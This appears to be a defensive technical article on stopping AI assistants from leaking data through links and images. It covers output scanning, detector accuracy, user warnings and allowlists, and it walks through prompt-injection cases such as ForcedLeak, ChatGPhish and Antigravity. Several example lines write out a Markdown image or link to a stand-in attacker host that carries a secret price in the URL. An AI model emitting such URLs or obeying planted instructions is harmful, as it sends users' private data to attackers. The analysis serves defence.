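Google and Anthropic both treat the user's message as a trustworthy origin. This is sensible for an address that Dana types or pastes. The address may contain a secret, such as a private link to a document, but she has chosen to have the assistant open it. The request also goes to the service that issued the link.

Not everything in a user's message comes from the user, though. In Samoilenko's original attack on ChatGPT, the victim unknowingly pasted in the hostile text. Oasis Security's *Claude.ai Prompt Injection to Data Exfiltration* describes a newer attack in which an ordinary-looking link opened Claude with the attacker's hidden instructions. VPNCentral's *Claude flaws could have exposed chat data* reports that the injection flaw has since been fixed. An application that approved every address in such a message would also approve any that the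 attacker had included.

An address that arrives this way can't contain Dana's price, because the attacker wrote it before the assistant read her mail. Opening it would still tell the attacker that someone had used the link. If each copy had a different address, the attacker would also learn who had used it. The attacker can also supply many addresses at once, which gives the model more to choose from.

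Results from other tools raise a similar problem. When Anthropic introduced the fetch tool, Willison (2025) was disappointed that the software around the model accepted addresses from tool results as well as from the user's prompts. If the developer's software retrieves Dana's mail, every address in the attacker's email arrives in a tool result and becomes acceptable. OpenAI is stricter about email. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, after an attack called ZombieAgent it restricted links from emails to those that qualify, for example by appearing in a well-known public index.

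A developer's own tools could defeat the rule, because Anthropic's ban on addresses from code execution covers only Anthropic's tools. If one of the developer's tools runs programs or returns the text it receives, the model could send it the attacker's host name and Dana's price and get back a complete address. The fetch tool would then accept that address because it appeared in a tool's output. Developers should treat the output of such tools as if the model had written it.

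The same thing can happen when one agent gives work to another. Many systems pass the task to the second agent as a user message, although the first agent's model wrote it. If that model has followed the instructions in Dana's email, the task may include the address with her price in it, and the second agent's software will treat the address as one a user typed. To prevent this, the developer can give the second agent the first agent's list of approved addresses and add none from the text of the task.

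## Scanning the output for sensitive data and suspicious links

Output scanning, also called output data-loss prevention (output DLP), examines the text of an answer, whereas rules about destinations and origins only control which addresses a viewer may contact. Companies have long used similar software on outgoing email to stop employees from sending out customers' card numbers.

### Leaks that no destination rule catches

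Suppose Dana's firm also runs a chatbot for its customers, and one customer's question leads it to print another customer's bank details. The data has leaked to the person reading the screen. The browser contacts no outside server, so an image filter or an allowlist has nothing to block. If the company's permission checks have failed, a scanner that recognises bank details can still catch the mistake.

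Secrets can also leak in plain text, long after the answer appears. A developer might ask an assistant to write public instructions for a program, and the assistant might copy a working API key into them from a configuration file. Once the instructions are published, anyone who reads them can use the key.

Some harmful links also pass every check on their destination. Many approved sites let anyone publish files and forms, so an allowlist would not block a fake login page on one of them. A check on the exact address would also miss it if the page had turned up in a search. Only information about the page itself, such as a report from an earlier victim, shows that it is dangerous.

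### How detectors recognise sensitive data

The simplest detector is a pattern that describes the shape of the data, such as sixteen digits in groups of four. Order numbers and parcel numbers can have the same shape. For payment cards, a scanner can rule out most of these with the Luhn check, a piece of arithmetic that card numbers satisfy:

1. Starting from the right, double every second digit.
2. If a doubled digit comes to more than nine, subtract nine.
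3. Add up all the digits. The number passes if the total is a multiple of ten.

Here is the check on a number that payment companies use for testing:

```
Card number:    4 1 1 1   1 1 1 1   1 1 1 1   1 1 1 1
After step 2:   8 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1   2 1 2 1
Total:          12 + 6 + 6 + 6 = 30, so the number passes
```

The number 1234 5678 9012 3456 gives a total of 64 and fails. The check removes about 90% of random lookalikes, and the rest pass by chance.

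A checksum can't show what a number is for. In *Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels*, Hsu and Berlin (2026) describe a detector for personally identifiable information (PII) that they built at Cisco. In one example, a sentence gives the test number above as an order number. The number passes the Luhn check, but the detector should ignore it because the sentence doesn't mention a card. The detector should flag a number that someone presents as a card number even if it fails the check, and leave the checksum to a later step.

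Names and street addresses have no fixed format, so scanners find them with named-entity models, which learn from examples to label people, places and organisations by the words around them. Presidio, a free tool that Microsoft originally developed, combines these models with patterns. According to *Hardening x402* (2026), Presidio's patterns give a match a score of 0.85 or 1.0, depending on whether a checksum confirms it, and the operator sets a minimum score. The scores are rough weights, so 0.85 does not mean an 85% chance that the match is right.

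Exact matching looks for specific records that a company holds. A program puts each value into a standard form, computes a short code called a fingerprint, and stores only the fingerprints. The scanner processes values in the answer the same way and compares the fingerprints. A match shows which record the value came from and what kind of data it is. Short values can cause false matches, because a tender price such as "482000" could appear in an answer for many innocent reasons. The company could require the price and the name of the tender to appear together. It should also use a secret key when computing fingerprints, since otherwise anyone who stole the list could try every six-digit number until one matched.

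API keys, which act as passwords for software, are easier to spot because many services give them a recognisable beginning and a fixed length. AWS's *Remove PII from conversations by using sensitive information filters* lists both halves of an AWS key pair among the built-in types that Bedrock Guardrails, Amazon's set of filters for AI applications, can detect. Google Cloud's *Model Armor overview* describes a competing product whose basic setting looks for Google Cloud credentials and API keys. Neither list includes the other company's keys, so a developer who uses both clouds has to add patterns. *SurrogateShield* (2026), which presents a rival to Presidio, reports that Presidio does not look for API keys, 32 of which appeared in the paper's test data.

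The last kind of detector looks for a marker string, a made-up value that someone has planted where no legitimate answer would need it. For example, Dana's firm could put a false password in a document that nobody uses, so that an answer containing the password would show that something has gone wrong.

In *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries*, Raz, Putrevu and colleagues (2026) hid identifiers in documents using invisible characters, lookalike letters and word choice, so that an AI service could recognise a stolen document when someone uploaded it. They recovered every identifier after ordinary handling and clean-up, with no false alarms. Their best design still recovered 97% after changes aimed at destroying the marks, but a poor combination of methods recovered none. These results apply to uploads, where the document arrives more or less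 whole. An assistant that summarises a document writes new sentences, so hidden marks would probably disappear. A visible false password has a better chance of surviving, because an attacker seeking passwords wants it copied exactly.

### Data the user may see and the server may not

Dana has every right to know the price in her firm's tender. The attacker's server has none. The same six digits can therefore be harmless in one line of an answer and a leak in the next:

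```
Our latest tender is priced at 482000.
![logo](https://img.attacker.example/logo.png?v=482000)
```

A scanner that applies one rule to the whole answer gets one of these lines wrong. If it masks the price everywhere, the assistant can't answer Dana's question, but if it allows the price everywhere because Dana is authorized to see it, the image sends the price to the attacker. *Towards Contextual Sensitive Data Detection* (2025) criticises both Google Cloud's DLP service and Presidio for treating any match with a known pattern as sensitive, whatever the context.

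An application can deal with this by separating the two parts of the answer according to who will receive them:

```
separate the addresses from the visible text

for each sensitive item in the visible text:
    if the reader may not see the record it came from:
        mask the item

for each address:
    split it into host name, path and query
    decode each part
    if any part contains a sensitive item:
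        remove the whole address
```

Dana's permissions don't matter in the rule for addresses because she doesn't receive the request. Visible text has to be checked against the permissions of its actual reader, so if the assistant emails its summary to a supplier, the application has to check what the supplier may see.

That check requires knowing which record an item came from. A pattern match shows only that something looks like a phone number, while an exact match identifies the customer. Without fingerprints, the application can keep a list of the documents the model used and check the reader's access to each. Microsoft avoids much of the problem in Copilot by running every request with the user's permissions, so Copilot shows people only material they could have opened themselves. This doesn't stop URLs in the output from sending that material elsewhere.

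The rule for URLs will also remove some legitimate links. A map link may contain Dana's home address, and an airline's check-in link usually contains a booking code. An application could exempt URLs that the model copied unchanged from a search result.

Detectors that work well on ordinary sentences may work badly on URLs. Hsu and Berlin compared their model with two others on finding IP addresses, the numbers that identify machines on the internet. Their model found 99% and the others found 72% and 65% by their own labels, which count IP addresses inside URLs. The others found over 99% and 92% by the dataset's original labels, which mostly leave those cases out. An attacker will seldom be after an IP address, but the difference suggests that some detectors treat a URL as a single item and overlook its contents. *Adaptive PII Mitigation Framework for Large Language Models* (2025), which also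 presents its own tool, reports that Amazon's Comprehend service missed email addresses inside hyperlinks.

Splitting the address into parts should help, though it removes the context that named-entity models rely on. AWS advises developers against giving its filter single words or short phrases, and nothing in "v=482000" suggests that the number is a price. Patterns and exact matching work better on such short parts. If the application uses Model Armor, it also has to decode the parts itself, because Model Armor does not decode URL encoding, hexadecimal or Base64.

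### Safe Browsing and new domains

Google removes links from Gemini's answers if Safe Browsing flags them as unsafe. According to Google's guide for administrators, Gemini also scans the files and emails a user refers to for suspicious links and planted instructions, and leaves out anything suspicious before writing an answer. If it leaves out only some of the messages, the user sees "Some content was excluded for security reasons", so Dana would know that her summary was incomplete.

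Model Armor gives developers a similar filter, with two differences. Its blocking mode withholds an entire answer if it contains one known phishing link, whereas Gemini removes the link and keeps the summary. Model Armor also checks only the first 256 addresses it finds, so an application that relies on it should cut off or refuse answers with more.

A reputation service misses new domains because it can list a site only after it has evidence, such as malware, a fake login page or complaints from victims. In the kind of leak in Dana's example, the domain could go unlisted for years, because the attacker's server can return an ordinary logo to every visitor, including any automated inspector, and the theft is visible only in the server's private log.

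Google gives no figure for how many harmful links its check catches. There also seems to be no public measurement of how often reputation lists miss servers that exist only to collect data. The lists are more useful against phishing, where the page has to look like a bank's website or a login screen and many people receive the same address.

### Mask, block, warn or log

When a scanner finds sensitive data, the application can mask it with a placeholder, so the reader still gets the rest of the answer. Bedrock Guardrails uses the type of data as the placeholder, such as "{EMAIL}". Masking works well in visible text, but it is safer to remove a suspicious URL completely, because the scanner may mask one part of it and miss data in another.

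Blocking replaces the answer with a message the developer has written. It makes sense when the whole answer is suspect or when the application has no reason to handle private data. AWS gives the example of a service that uses public documents to answer general questions.

A warning leaves the decision to the user. For an image, the application has to hold back the request until the user responds, or the data will already have been sent by the time the warning appears.

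Logging records the finding without acting on it, so a company can see how many false alarms a rule would cause before enforcing it. AWS's *Options for handling harmful content detected by Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* recommends its log-only setting for this purpose, and Google Cloud also advises customers to start without blocking. A company can easily forget to turn on blocking later. Microsoft's default policy for Copilot starts in simulation mode, so an administrator who leaves it alone gets a record of sensitive prompts but no protection.

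Masking sensitive data in the displayed answer doesn't remove it from other copies. If a customer turns on logging in Bedrock, the log keeps the user's original request even when the filter masks part of it for the model. The detection report that Bedrock returns to the application also contains the original value. If a customer enables Model Armor's logs, they can contain extracts from the text too. Log viewers should show these logs as plain text, like any other viewer of stored answers.

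### Scanning while the model is still writing

No detector can recognise a card number from its first four digits, so a scanner has to hold back part of a streamed answer to catch the number before it is displayed. AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content* describes two modes for Bedrock Guardrails. The default mode holds each piece of text until it has been scanned. The other mode sends text immediately and scans in the background, blocking whatever comes after the first problem it finds. This second mode can't mask personal data and may act too late to stop an image leak.

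Google Cloud's *Sanitize prompts and responses* describes two modes for Model Armor. One collects the whole text and checks it together, up to a length limit. The other checks each piece separately as it arrives and has no such limit.

A scanner that checks output in separate pieces can miss sensitive data split between two of them. AWS's *StreamingConfigurations* gives 50 characters as the default interval at which Bedrock's agents apply the filter. If a scanner cut the text into 50-character pieces and checked each one separately, a boundary would split a 19-character card number, including spaces, in 18 of 50 possible positions (36%). Keeping some of the earlier text and scanning it again with the next piece prevents this. Hsu and Berlin trained their model on overlapping pieces, each sharing a quarter of its length with the next.

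The detector adds little delay. In Hsu and Berlin's tests on a single graphics processor, four models took between 20 and 174 milliseconds for a typical input. Waiting for the text takes much longer. If the model takes 15 seconds to write an answer and the scanner needs the whole answer, Dana sees nothing for 15 seconds. Releasing one paragraph at a time would usually give the scanner enough context and cut the wait to a few seconds. An application that cleans Markdown before display already has to hold text back this way, so scanning the same blocks adds little to the wait.

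### Encoded and divided data

A pattern matches data by its format. Encoding changes that format, but the recipient can still decode the data. A scanner can reverse common encodings, but an attacker can plant instructions for the model to use one that nobody has used before.

Scanners can also miss sensitive data that is split into pieces. Half a card number doesn't match the pattern for a card, and the Luhn check only works on the full number. Model Armor examines each prompt and answer separately and keeps no history of the conversation, so it can't join pieces sent in different turns. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) describes an experiment in which splitting a secret across requests was enough to get past simple scanning.

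In standard tests, scanners also often miss partial or disguised mentions of personal data. *REDACT* (2026), a test of personal-data detectors in several languages, found that Presidio caught 2% of partial mentions and 7% of disguised ones.

### What the commercial products check

Companies use Microsoft Purview to control sensitive data across Microsoft's office programs. According to Microsoft's documentation as of April 2026, Purview checked the text that users typed into Copilot and could keep Copilot from using files and emails with a chosen label, such as "Highly Confidential". The documentation listed no scan of Copilot's finished answer.

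The check on typed text would not have helped Dana, because her request to summarise the morning's mail contained nothing sensitive. Microsoft describes the check as a way to stop Copilot from processing sensitive data that employees put into their prompts, which is a different problem. Labels would have worked if her firm had labelled the email containing the tender and set Purview to exclude that label. The attacker would then have got nothing, but Dana could not have asked Copilot about the tender either. The label rule also doesn't cover calendar invitations or emails sent before 2025.

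cloudmagazin (2026), a trade publication, reported in May that Purview could now evaluate agents' responses as well as prompts. If so, Purview has added a check on output that the April documentation did not list.

Bedrock Guardrails scans a model's answers, but not the values that the model passes to a tool. AWS gives the example of a customer's email address that the model sends to a tool for writing files. The filter would also miss Dana's price if the model put it into a URL and passed that URL to a tool for fetching web pages. A developer has to scan those values separately.

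Model Armor's basic setting can detect six types of data, including card numbers and US Social Security numbers, but can't mask them. The advanced setting accepts the customer's own definitions and can mask what it finds. None of these products includes tender prices as a standard type, so Dana's firm would have to write a rule for its own secrets whichever one it bought.

| Product | What the vendor documents | Public accuracy test |
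|---|---|---|
| Purview for Copilot | Checks typed prompts; excludes labelled files and emails | None apparent |
| Model Armor | Scans prompts and answers for sensitive data and known harmful links | None apparent, but researchers have tested Google's DLP service |
| Bedrock Guardrails | Scans the text of prompts and answers, but not values passed to tools | None apparent |
| Presidio | Patterns, checksums and a named-entity model | Several, with very different results |

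The vendors describe accuracy but publish no measurements of it. Google Cloud's guide calls the risk of false alarms "very low" at Model Armor's strictest confidence setting but gives no number. Gavish says that Google simulates attacks on its office products with each defense turned on and then off. This is a sound way to measure what the defense adds, but the article includes no results.

### Measured accuracy

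Researchers usually report a detector's recall, the share of sensitive items it finds, and its precision, the share of its alarms that are correct. A detector that flagged every word would have perfect recall but very low precision.

*Data Quality in RVL-CDIP* (Larson and Leach, 2026) tested four detectors on 1,773 scanned documents from lawsuits against tobacco companies. Presidio found 97% of the Social Security numbers, Google's DLP service 93%, Amazon Comprehend 77%, and Microsoft's Azure language service 70%. Social Security numbers have a fixed format, so a miss rate of up to 30% is high, although errors in reading the old scans may account for some of the misses. Model Armor uses Google's DLP technology, now called Sensitive Data Protection, so the 93% is indirect evidence about Model Armor. The Amazon and Azure figures are weaker evidence about Bedrock Guardrails and Purview, which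 are separate products.

Larson and Leach also found that seven of the eleven types of sensitive data they had recorded could not be detected by any of the four tools. The tools that looked for phone numbers and addresses couldn't tell whether these belonged to a person's home or an office.

Other researchers have tested Presidio on varied material. *Mind the Gap* (2026) ran it on two different kinds of text. *Reconstruction of Personally Identifiable Information from Proprietary Data in Supervised Fine-Tuned Models* (2026) used it to mask personal data in two datasets. *Utility-Preserving De-Identification for Math Tutoring* (2026) tested it on tutoring sessions, which contain many harmless numbers. *PIIBench* (2026) combined several public datasets and counted a detection as correct only if it had the right type and the exact start and end.

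| Test | Presidio's result |
|---|---|
| *Mind the Gap* | Recall 89%, falling to 78% on the second set; precision 76% and 74% |
| *Reconstruction of Personally Identifiable Information from Proprietary Data in Supervised Fine-Tuned Models* | Every email address found, with no false alarms; every date found, but with 13% precision |
| *Utility-Preserving De-Identification for Math Tutoring* | Recall 75%, precision 25% |
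| *PIIBench* | Recall 13%, precision 15%, the best overall score of eight systems |
| *REDACT* | Recall 7% on the most sensitive items |

Some of this spread comes from the scoring. *PIIBench* counts masking most of a name as a failure, even though it is still useful. The rest mostly comes from the kind of data. Presidio does well with email addresses and Social Security numbers and badly with anything that depends on meaning. Two general-purpose language models, GPT-4.1 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, found 74% and 77% of *REDACT*'s most sensitive items. In the tutoring sessions, language models had about the same recall as Presidio and up to 90% fewer false alarms. Running a language model on every answer costs more, so a company might use a fast detector first and send only the doubtful cases to the model.

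The same detector can perform very differently on different tests. Hsu and Berlin adjusted each model so that, for any one type of data, it wrongly flagged at most 0.1% of 100,000 real chatbot conversations. At that setting, a model from the company Fastino found 97.5% of the card numbers in one dataset and 57% in another. Cisco's own model scored higher on both, but the labels followed the definitions that Cisco had trained it on. A company choosing a scanner would learn more from a trial on its own conversations than from either figure.

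### A million answers a day

Real leaks are rare, so even a low false alarm rate can produce far more false alarms than detected leaks. Suppose an assistant gives a million answers a day, ten of which leak data, and a scanner detects 95% of leaks and wrongly flags 0.5% of harmless answers. On average, it would flag about 5,000 harmless answers a day and detect 9.5 leaks.

```
Leaks caught:    10 × 95%         = 9.5
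False alarms:    999,990 × 0.5%   = about 5,000
```

The scanner raises about 5,000 false alarms to catch nine or ten leaks, so only about one alarm in 527 is real. Spending one minute on each alarm would take more than ten full-time reviewers, who would probably start dismissing alarms without reading them. Scanning for more types of data can produce more false alarms. At Hsu and Berlin's limit of 0.1% for each type, a detector for twelve types could wrongly flag up to 12,000 answers a day.

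Real data can produce similar proportions. *Personal Information Parroting in Language Models* (2026) used patterns to search a large collection of text for phone numbers and got 1.28 million matches. From a sample checked by hand, the paper estimated that about 278,000 were real.

The harm from a false alarm depends on how the application responds. If it automatically removes one link, one user in every 200 loses a link, which would be acceptable for most products. If it withholds the whole answer, 5,000 people a day get no answer.

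The company can also scan fewer answers. Suppose only 20,000 of the million contain an outside address that the model might have composed, and all ten leaks are among them. If the same scanner checked only those addresses, it would raise about 100 false alarms, and roughly one alarm in twelve would be real. A small team could review that many. The 95% detection rate would still apply only to leaks like those in the scanner's tests, and an attacker who encodes the data could lower that rate considerably without changing the number of false alarms.

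## Leaving the decision to the user

A scanner that removes suspicious links will sometimes remove harmless ones. An application can instead keep a suspicious link, explain the problem, and let the user decide whether to open it.

Leaving the decision to the user makes most sense for assistants that cite sources. Dana has to open the official tender rules to check that the assistant summarised them correctly. She may also have information that no filter has, for example that an unfamiliar site belongs to a new supplier. Browsers and mail programs already let people choose whether to follow links to unknown sites.

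An assistant under an attacker's influence can put Dana's price into the address of a link in its answer. The sender of an ordinary email can't do this, because they write the link without seeing her mailbox. People are used to asking whether a site looks trustworthy, but few would think to ask whether the address contains their own data.

The argument that the user can choose also doesn't apply to remote images or the link previews that PromptArmor warns about, because both send the address before Dana can decide.

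### Reports that vendors closed without a fix

On 5 October 2025, Checkmarx told Google that a link in a Gemini answer could send private data to any server if the user clicked it. According to Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, Google closed the report four days later as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". Google replied that the problem was not severe enough to track as a security bug, and that it pays rewards only for flaws that "substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity of user data". Checkmarx accepted this but thought users should then get a warning. Gemini now records where each address came from and blocks links that the model composed, so at least a partial fix was feasible.

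On 15 October, Checkmarx reported a more serious problem to Microsoft, a zero-click leak in Copilot Chat. In the demonstration, planted instructions led the assistant to put an API key from the developer's computer into an image address. No image appeared, but the request still reached the researchers' server.

Microsoft replied on 4 November that this was not a vulnerability, for four reasons:

- The attack needs several user actions that are not the default.
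- It does not work reliably in every environment.
- The product displays warnings meant to reduce the risk.
- Under a principle the letter calls "Workplace Trust", Microsoft assumes that users review and trust the code they choose to run.

Checkmarx gives no success rate, so outsiders can't judge the point about reliability. It concedes that getting the assistant to read a hostile page can be complicated, which partly supports Microsoft's first reason. The fourth reason fits the attack badly because, by Checkmarx's account, the instructions could be in an online article, where a developer who carefully reviewed every line of code would still miss them.

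Microsoft said it had passed the report to its engineers, who would look for ways to make the behavior clearer to users. It does not appear to have reclassified the leak since. But Microsoft and its subsidiary GitHub have treated similar leaks as flaws. Willison (2024) recorded that GitHub fixed one in Copilot Chat by blocking images from untrusted domains. Version 1.100.1 of VS Code, Microsoft's code editor, stopped displaying remote images in chat altogether, according to a security advisory. Both changes came before Checkmarx's report, so Microsoft's letter looks more like a judgement on one demonstration than a policy that image leaks are acceptable.

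Google gave researchers inconsistent answers about Antigravity, its coding tool. Willison relates that a researcher who reported the image leak in November 2025 said Google had marked it as "intended behavior". According to Deadbits' *Indirect Prompt Injection in AI IDEs* (2025), Google replied to a report of a related flaw by saying the behavior was expected, already known, and outside the reward program. In its public list of known issues, quoted in a discussion on Brian Lovin's website, Google acknowledged that the agent could leak files through URLs in Markdown and that nothing enforced the agent's caution with sensitive files. Willison adds that Google was working on fixes, which seems inconsistent with calling the leak intended.

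Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* suggests that Google inherited the flaw rather than chose it. Google had built Antigravity on code licensed from Windsurf, another editor, and Rehberger had reported the same leak to Windsurf in May 2025. In the meantime, Google relied on a disclaimer about the risks, according to PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*.

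The promised fix was slow. The news site CyberScoop reports that Google patched a different Antigravity flaw, which let attackers run code, within two months of receiving a report in January 2026, but the image leak still worked in June. Willison recommends that developers who use such tools anyway give the agent only passwords and keys for test accounts with strict spending limits, so that a theft does little damage.

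### What the user sees before a link opens

The simplest aid is to print the full address next to the link's text. This tells Dana where the link leads, but it only sometimes tells her what it carries:

```
the tender (https://img.attacker.example/t?v=482000)
the tender (https://img.attacker.example/t?v=NDgyMDAw)
```

She might recognise her price in the first address. The second contains the same price in Base64, a common encoding, and looks like the codes in many ordinary links. The host name is easier to read, but it helps only if she knows which site to expect. If the link uses a link-shortening service, she sees the service's host name instead of the destination's.

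Some products make links unclickable, so the user has to copy the address and paste it into the browser. This prevents accidental clicks and gives Dana time to read the address, but it doesn't help if she copies it without reading. She could also leak the price by being careful, because if she pasted the address into Slack to ask a colleague about it, the link preview would send the price to the attacker.

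Other products put a confirmation page between the click and the destination. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) describes how this works in Colab, Google's online notebook for writing and running code. Colab adds a Google address to the front of every link in the assistant's answers:

```
https://www.google.com/url?q=https://img.attacker.example/t?v=482000
```

A click contacts Google first, and Google asks the user to confirm. The attacker's server receives nothing unless the user continues.

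Rehberger found that links to Google's own domains skipped the confirmation page. One of those domains hosts Apps Script, where anyone can publish a small program, so Google's ownership of the domain did not mean that Google controlled the page. In his demonstration, planted instructions made the assistant ask for personal information and then offer a link labeled "I'm feeling lucky". Clicking it sent the user's name, email address and notebook code to Rehberger's program without a warning.

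When a link isn't in OpenAI's index of public addresses, ChatGPT displays a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". The dialog shows the address, which the user can copy or open, and a warning that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with a third-party site. If something looks wrong, OpenAI suggests asking ChatGPT for another source or a summary instead of opening the link.

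This design has two advantages over Colab's. The dialog warns the user that the address may contain their data, and it appears only when an automatic check fails, so most links to established pages open without it. However, Dana still has to spot her price in the address herself, and she would not spot it in the Base64 version.

VS Code asks more often, requiring the user to approve any address once per session before the chat's fetch tool opens it, whatever the domain. The developers previously skipped this step for trusted domains, but GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections* explains that their check accepted an unrelated site if ".github.com" appeared in the path. Users can turn on automatic approval, but this brings the original risk back.

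### A dangerous command that most developers approved

All these designs rely on people reading the warning. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026) reports a large experiment on a similar decision. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, can ask users for permission before it runs a command, and Anthropic wanted to compare their answers with those of an automated check called auto mode.

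A research company recruited 1,053 paid professional testers for what they understood to be a coding study. The testers worked in a test environment, not on their own projects, and knew they were being evaluated but not which behavior mattered. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded whether the tester approved it. They changed only the displayed text, so the dangerous command never ran.

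Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused the command. Auto mode blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands, or 89%. The overlap is informative too:

| | Auto mode blocked it | Auto mode allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused it | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved it | 800 | 110 |

The testers caught six of the 116 commands that auto mode let through. A human approving commands after the automated check would therefore have added very little protection in this experiment.

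Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This fits the idea that people stop reading repeated questions, although testers who reached 50 prompts may have differed from the others in ways that Anthropic doesn't describe. The idea also fits figures from real use, where users approve 97% of permission prompts and 62% have bypassed the prompts or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, which can do almost anything on a computer. Willison is skeptical of some of Anthropic's other claims about auto mode but agrees that "confirmation fatigue is real".

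Anthropic published these results to justify replacing the prompts with its own product, so it had an interest in the outcome. The test environment may also have made people careless, since they had no work of their own to lose. But Anthropic found a similar pattern in real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those with auto mode. Users choose their own mode, so differences between the users or their tasks may explain part of that gap.

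### From coding commands to links

The experiment is only indirect evidence about link warnings. A developer may see hundreds of permission prompts in a day, nearly all for harmless commands, and refusing one delays the work. Link warnings can be rare, and Dana loses little by refusing a link if the assistant can find another source. These differences suggest that people would refuse dangerous links more often than the testers refused dangerous commands.

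Dana's decision is harder in other ways. The testers were professionals, and anyone who read the command in front of them could see that it was dangerous. Dana works for a building firm, and an address with an encoded price looks like any other, so she could read the whole warning carefully and still make the wrong choice.

The wording and purpose of a dialog also matter. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans it presents for approval but only 3% of individual permission requests. The 39% shows that they don't approve everything by reflex, but it doesn't measure how well they spot danger, because they may reject a plan simply because they want something different.

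A direct test would give people real tasks in a chat window, include a few links that contain the user's data, and record how many of those links people open. It should also count how many harmless links they refuse, because a warning that scared people away from every link would prevent all of these leaks too. Varying the number of earlier warnings would show whether people really pay attention to a dialog they rarely see.

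Even a good refusal rate may not protect a secret that many people share. Suppose 20 of Dana's colleagues can see the tender price, the attacker emails all of them, and each sees a dangerous link. If each refuses it 95% of the time, independently of the others, the chance that at least one opens it is about 64%:

```
1 − 0.95^20 = 0.64
```

At the testers' refusal rate, the attacker would almost certainly succeed. A rule that blocks addresses the model composed avoids this problem because it gives the same result for all 20.

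### Warnings in the attacker's words

A careful user can still approve a leak if the question is misleading. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) demonstrated this with the image leak in Antigravity. The planted instructions presented the theft of an API key as a step in fixing a broken build. Antigravity then asked the user to approve "generating a visual debug token". The user agreed, but the question had included neither the command that would read the key nor the address that would receive it.

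This was a demonstration by the researchers, so it doesn't measure how often real users would agree. The design is still clearly flawed, because the model wrote the description of its own action after the attacker had influenced the model. Odson and Morris conclude that a permission prompt protects people only if it names the actual command and destination. Checkmarx has described similar attacks on human approval, which it calls "Lies-in-the-Loop", and warns that an attacker who controls the Markdown in an answer can make them more effective.

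### ChatGPhish

The text around a link can also mislead people. *ChatGPhish*, published by the security company Permiso on 29 May 2026, describes an attack through web pages that people ask ChatGPT to summarise. The researchers added instructions to the introductory page of a software project, opened it in Firefox, and requested a summary from the browser's menu. ChatGPT wrote a genuine summary, then added an account notice about a new device with a link to the researchers' site. The method also worked on an ordinary web page they hosted.

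Most people have learned to distrust such a notice in an email from a stranger, but this one appeared in ChatGPT's own window and formatting, below a correct summary. Nothing marked the link as coming from the web page, so a user could easily take the notice for a message from OpenAI.

In another version, ChatGPT displayed a QR code. Scanning it with a phone opens an address that the user has not seen as text. This bypasses the link preview on the desktop, the company's blocklists, and the password manager that would detect a login page on the wrong domain. Loading the image also sent the user's network address, browser type and the exact time of the answer to the researchers' server.

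Permiso's researchers chose the addresses in advance and did not show ChatGPT putting private data into one. A check for composed addresses could therefore approve them if the software treated the page's text as a trusted source of addresses. Firefox passes that text to ChatGPT, which reportedly accepts addresses in the user's message. This might explain why the pictures loaded, but Permiso doesn't establish the cause. The cause hardly matters for the fake notice, because the user loses a password by typing it into the attacker's page, and a warning about data in the URL would not address that risk.

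Permiso reported the attack to OpenAI through Bugcrowd on 29 April and was told the next day that the report lacked the details needed to reproduce it. Permiso sent a fuller version on 1 May, which was first marked "Not Applicable" and later marked a duplicate of an earlier report. The duplicate status suggests OpenAI already knew of the problem, but doesn't show whether it planned a fix. Two days after publication, eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* found no sign of a fix in the published timeline. It advised readers not to trust links, images or QR codes in AI summaries unless they could verify the source.

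An application can do some of that verification for the user. It can load no pictures in summaries, which removes the QR code, and list a page's links under the page's own name. For an address that fails the automatic checks, it could show Dana something like this:

```
The assistant wrote this address. It may contain your data.

Site:                  img.attacker.example
Text the site gets:    /t?v=482000
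Site name found in:    an email from an unknown sender

[Find another source]    [Copy address]    [Open anyway]
```

The application has to fill in these lines from the address it is about to open and from its own records, because the model's description could be false. It should decode common encodings such as Base64 so the price is readable. It should also display the dialog outside the answer, in a part of the window where the model can't write. Otherwise, planted instructions could make the model draw a convincing imitation of the dialog, with a notice that the link is safe.

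## Whether a list of trusted sites can be kept safe

When a warning appears, Dana has to judge an address in the middle of her work. With an allowlist, an administrator can make that judgement in advance, without an attacker's text on the screen. But in 2025 and 2026, researchers repeatedly got data out of AI products through approved sites.

People who favor lists blame these leaks on poorly maintained lists. Salesforce responded to one leak by correcting its list and applying it more widely, and PromptArmor advises administrators to approve each address explicitly. Critics doubt that maintenance is enough, because almost any large site has some feature that records or forwards what it receives. OpenAI stresses forwarding, and Willison calls finding domains that can't leak data "a tricky proposition".

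If poor upkeep is to blame, leaks should occur through entries that no longer belong on the list, such as a site that has changed hands. If the critics are right, leaks should also occur through sites that work as their owners intend.

Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* lists three things an attacker needs: an approved site, a way to send data to it in an ordinary page request, and a way to see what the site received. The person who emailed Dana can already send data to img.attacker.example and see what arrives there. With an allowlist in place, that person has to find a way to do both on an approved site that someone else runs.

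### A domain that nobody renewed

Salesforce's CSP let its pages load images from any host under my-salesforce-cms.com. The domain's registration expired, but the entry stayed in the policy. Researchers at the security company Noma then registered the domain, which cost $5 according to BeyondMachines.

Noma planted its instructions through Web-to-Lead, a Salesforce feature that saves submissions from a form on a company's public website as sales leads. When an employee asked Agentforce about Noma's submission, the agent wrote the email addresses of the company's leads into an image URL on the lapsed domain. The policy allowed that domain, so the browser requested the image from Noma's server. Noma called the attack ForcedLeak, and Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* reports a severity score of 9.4 out of 10.

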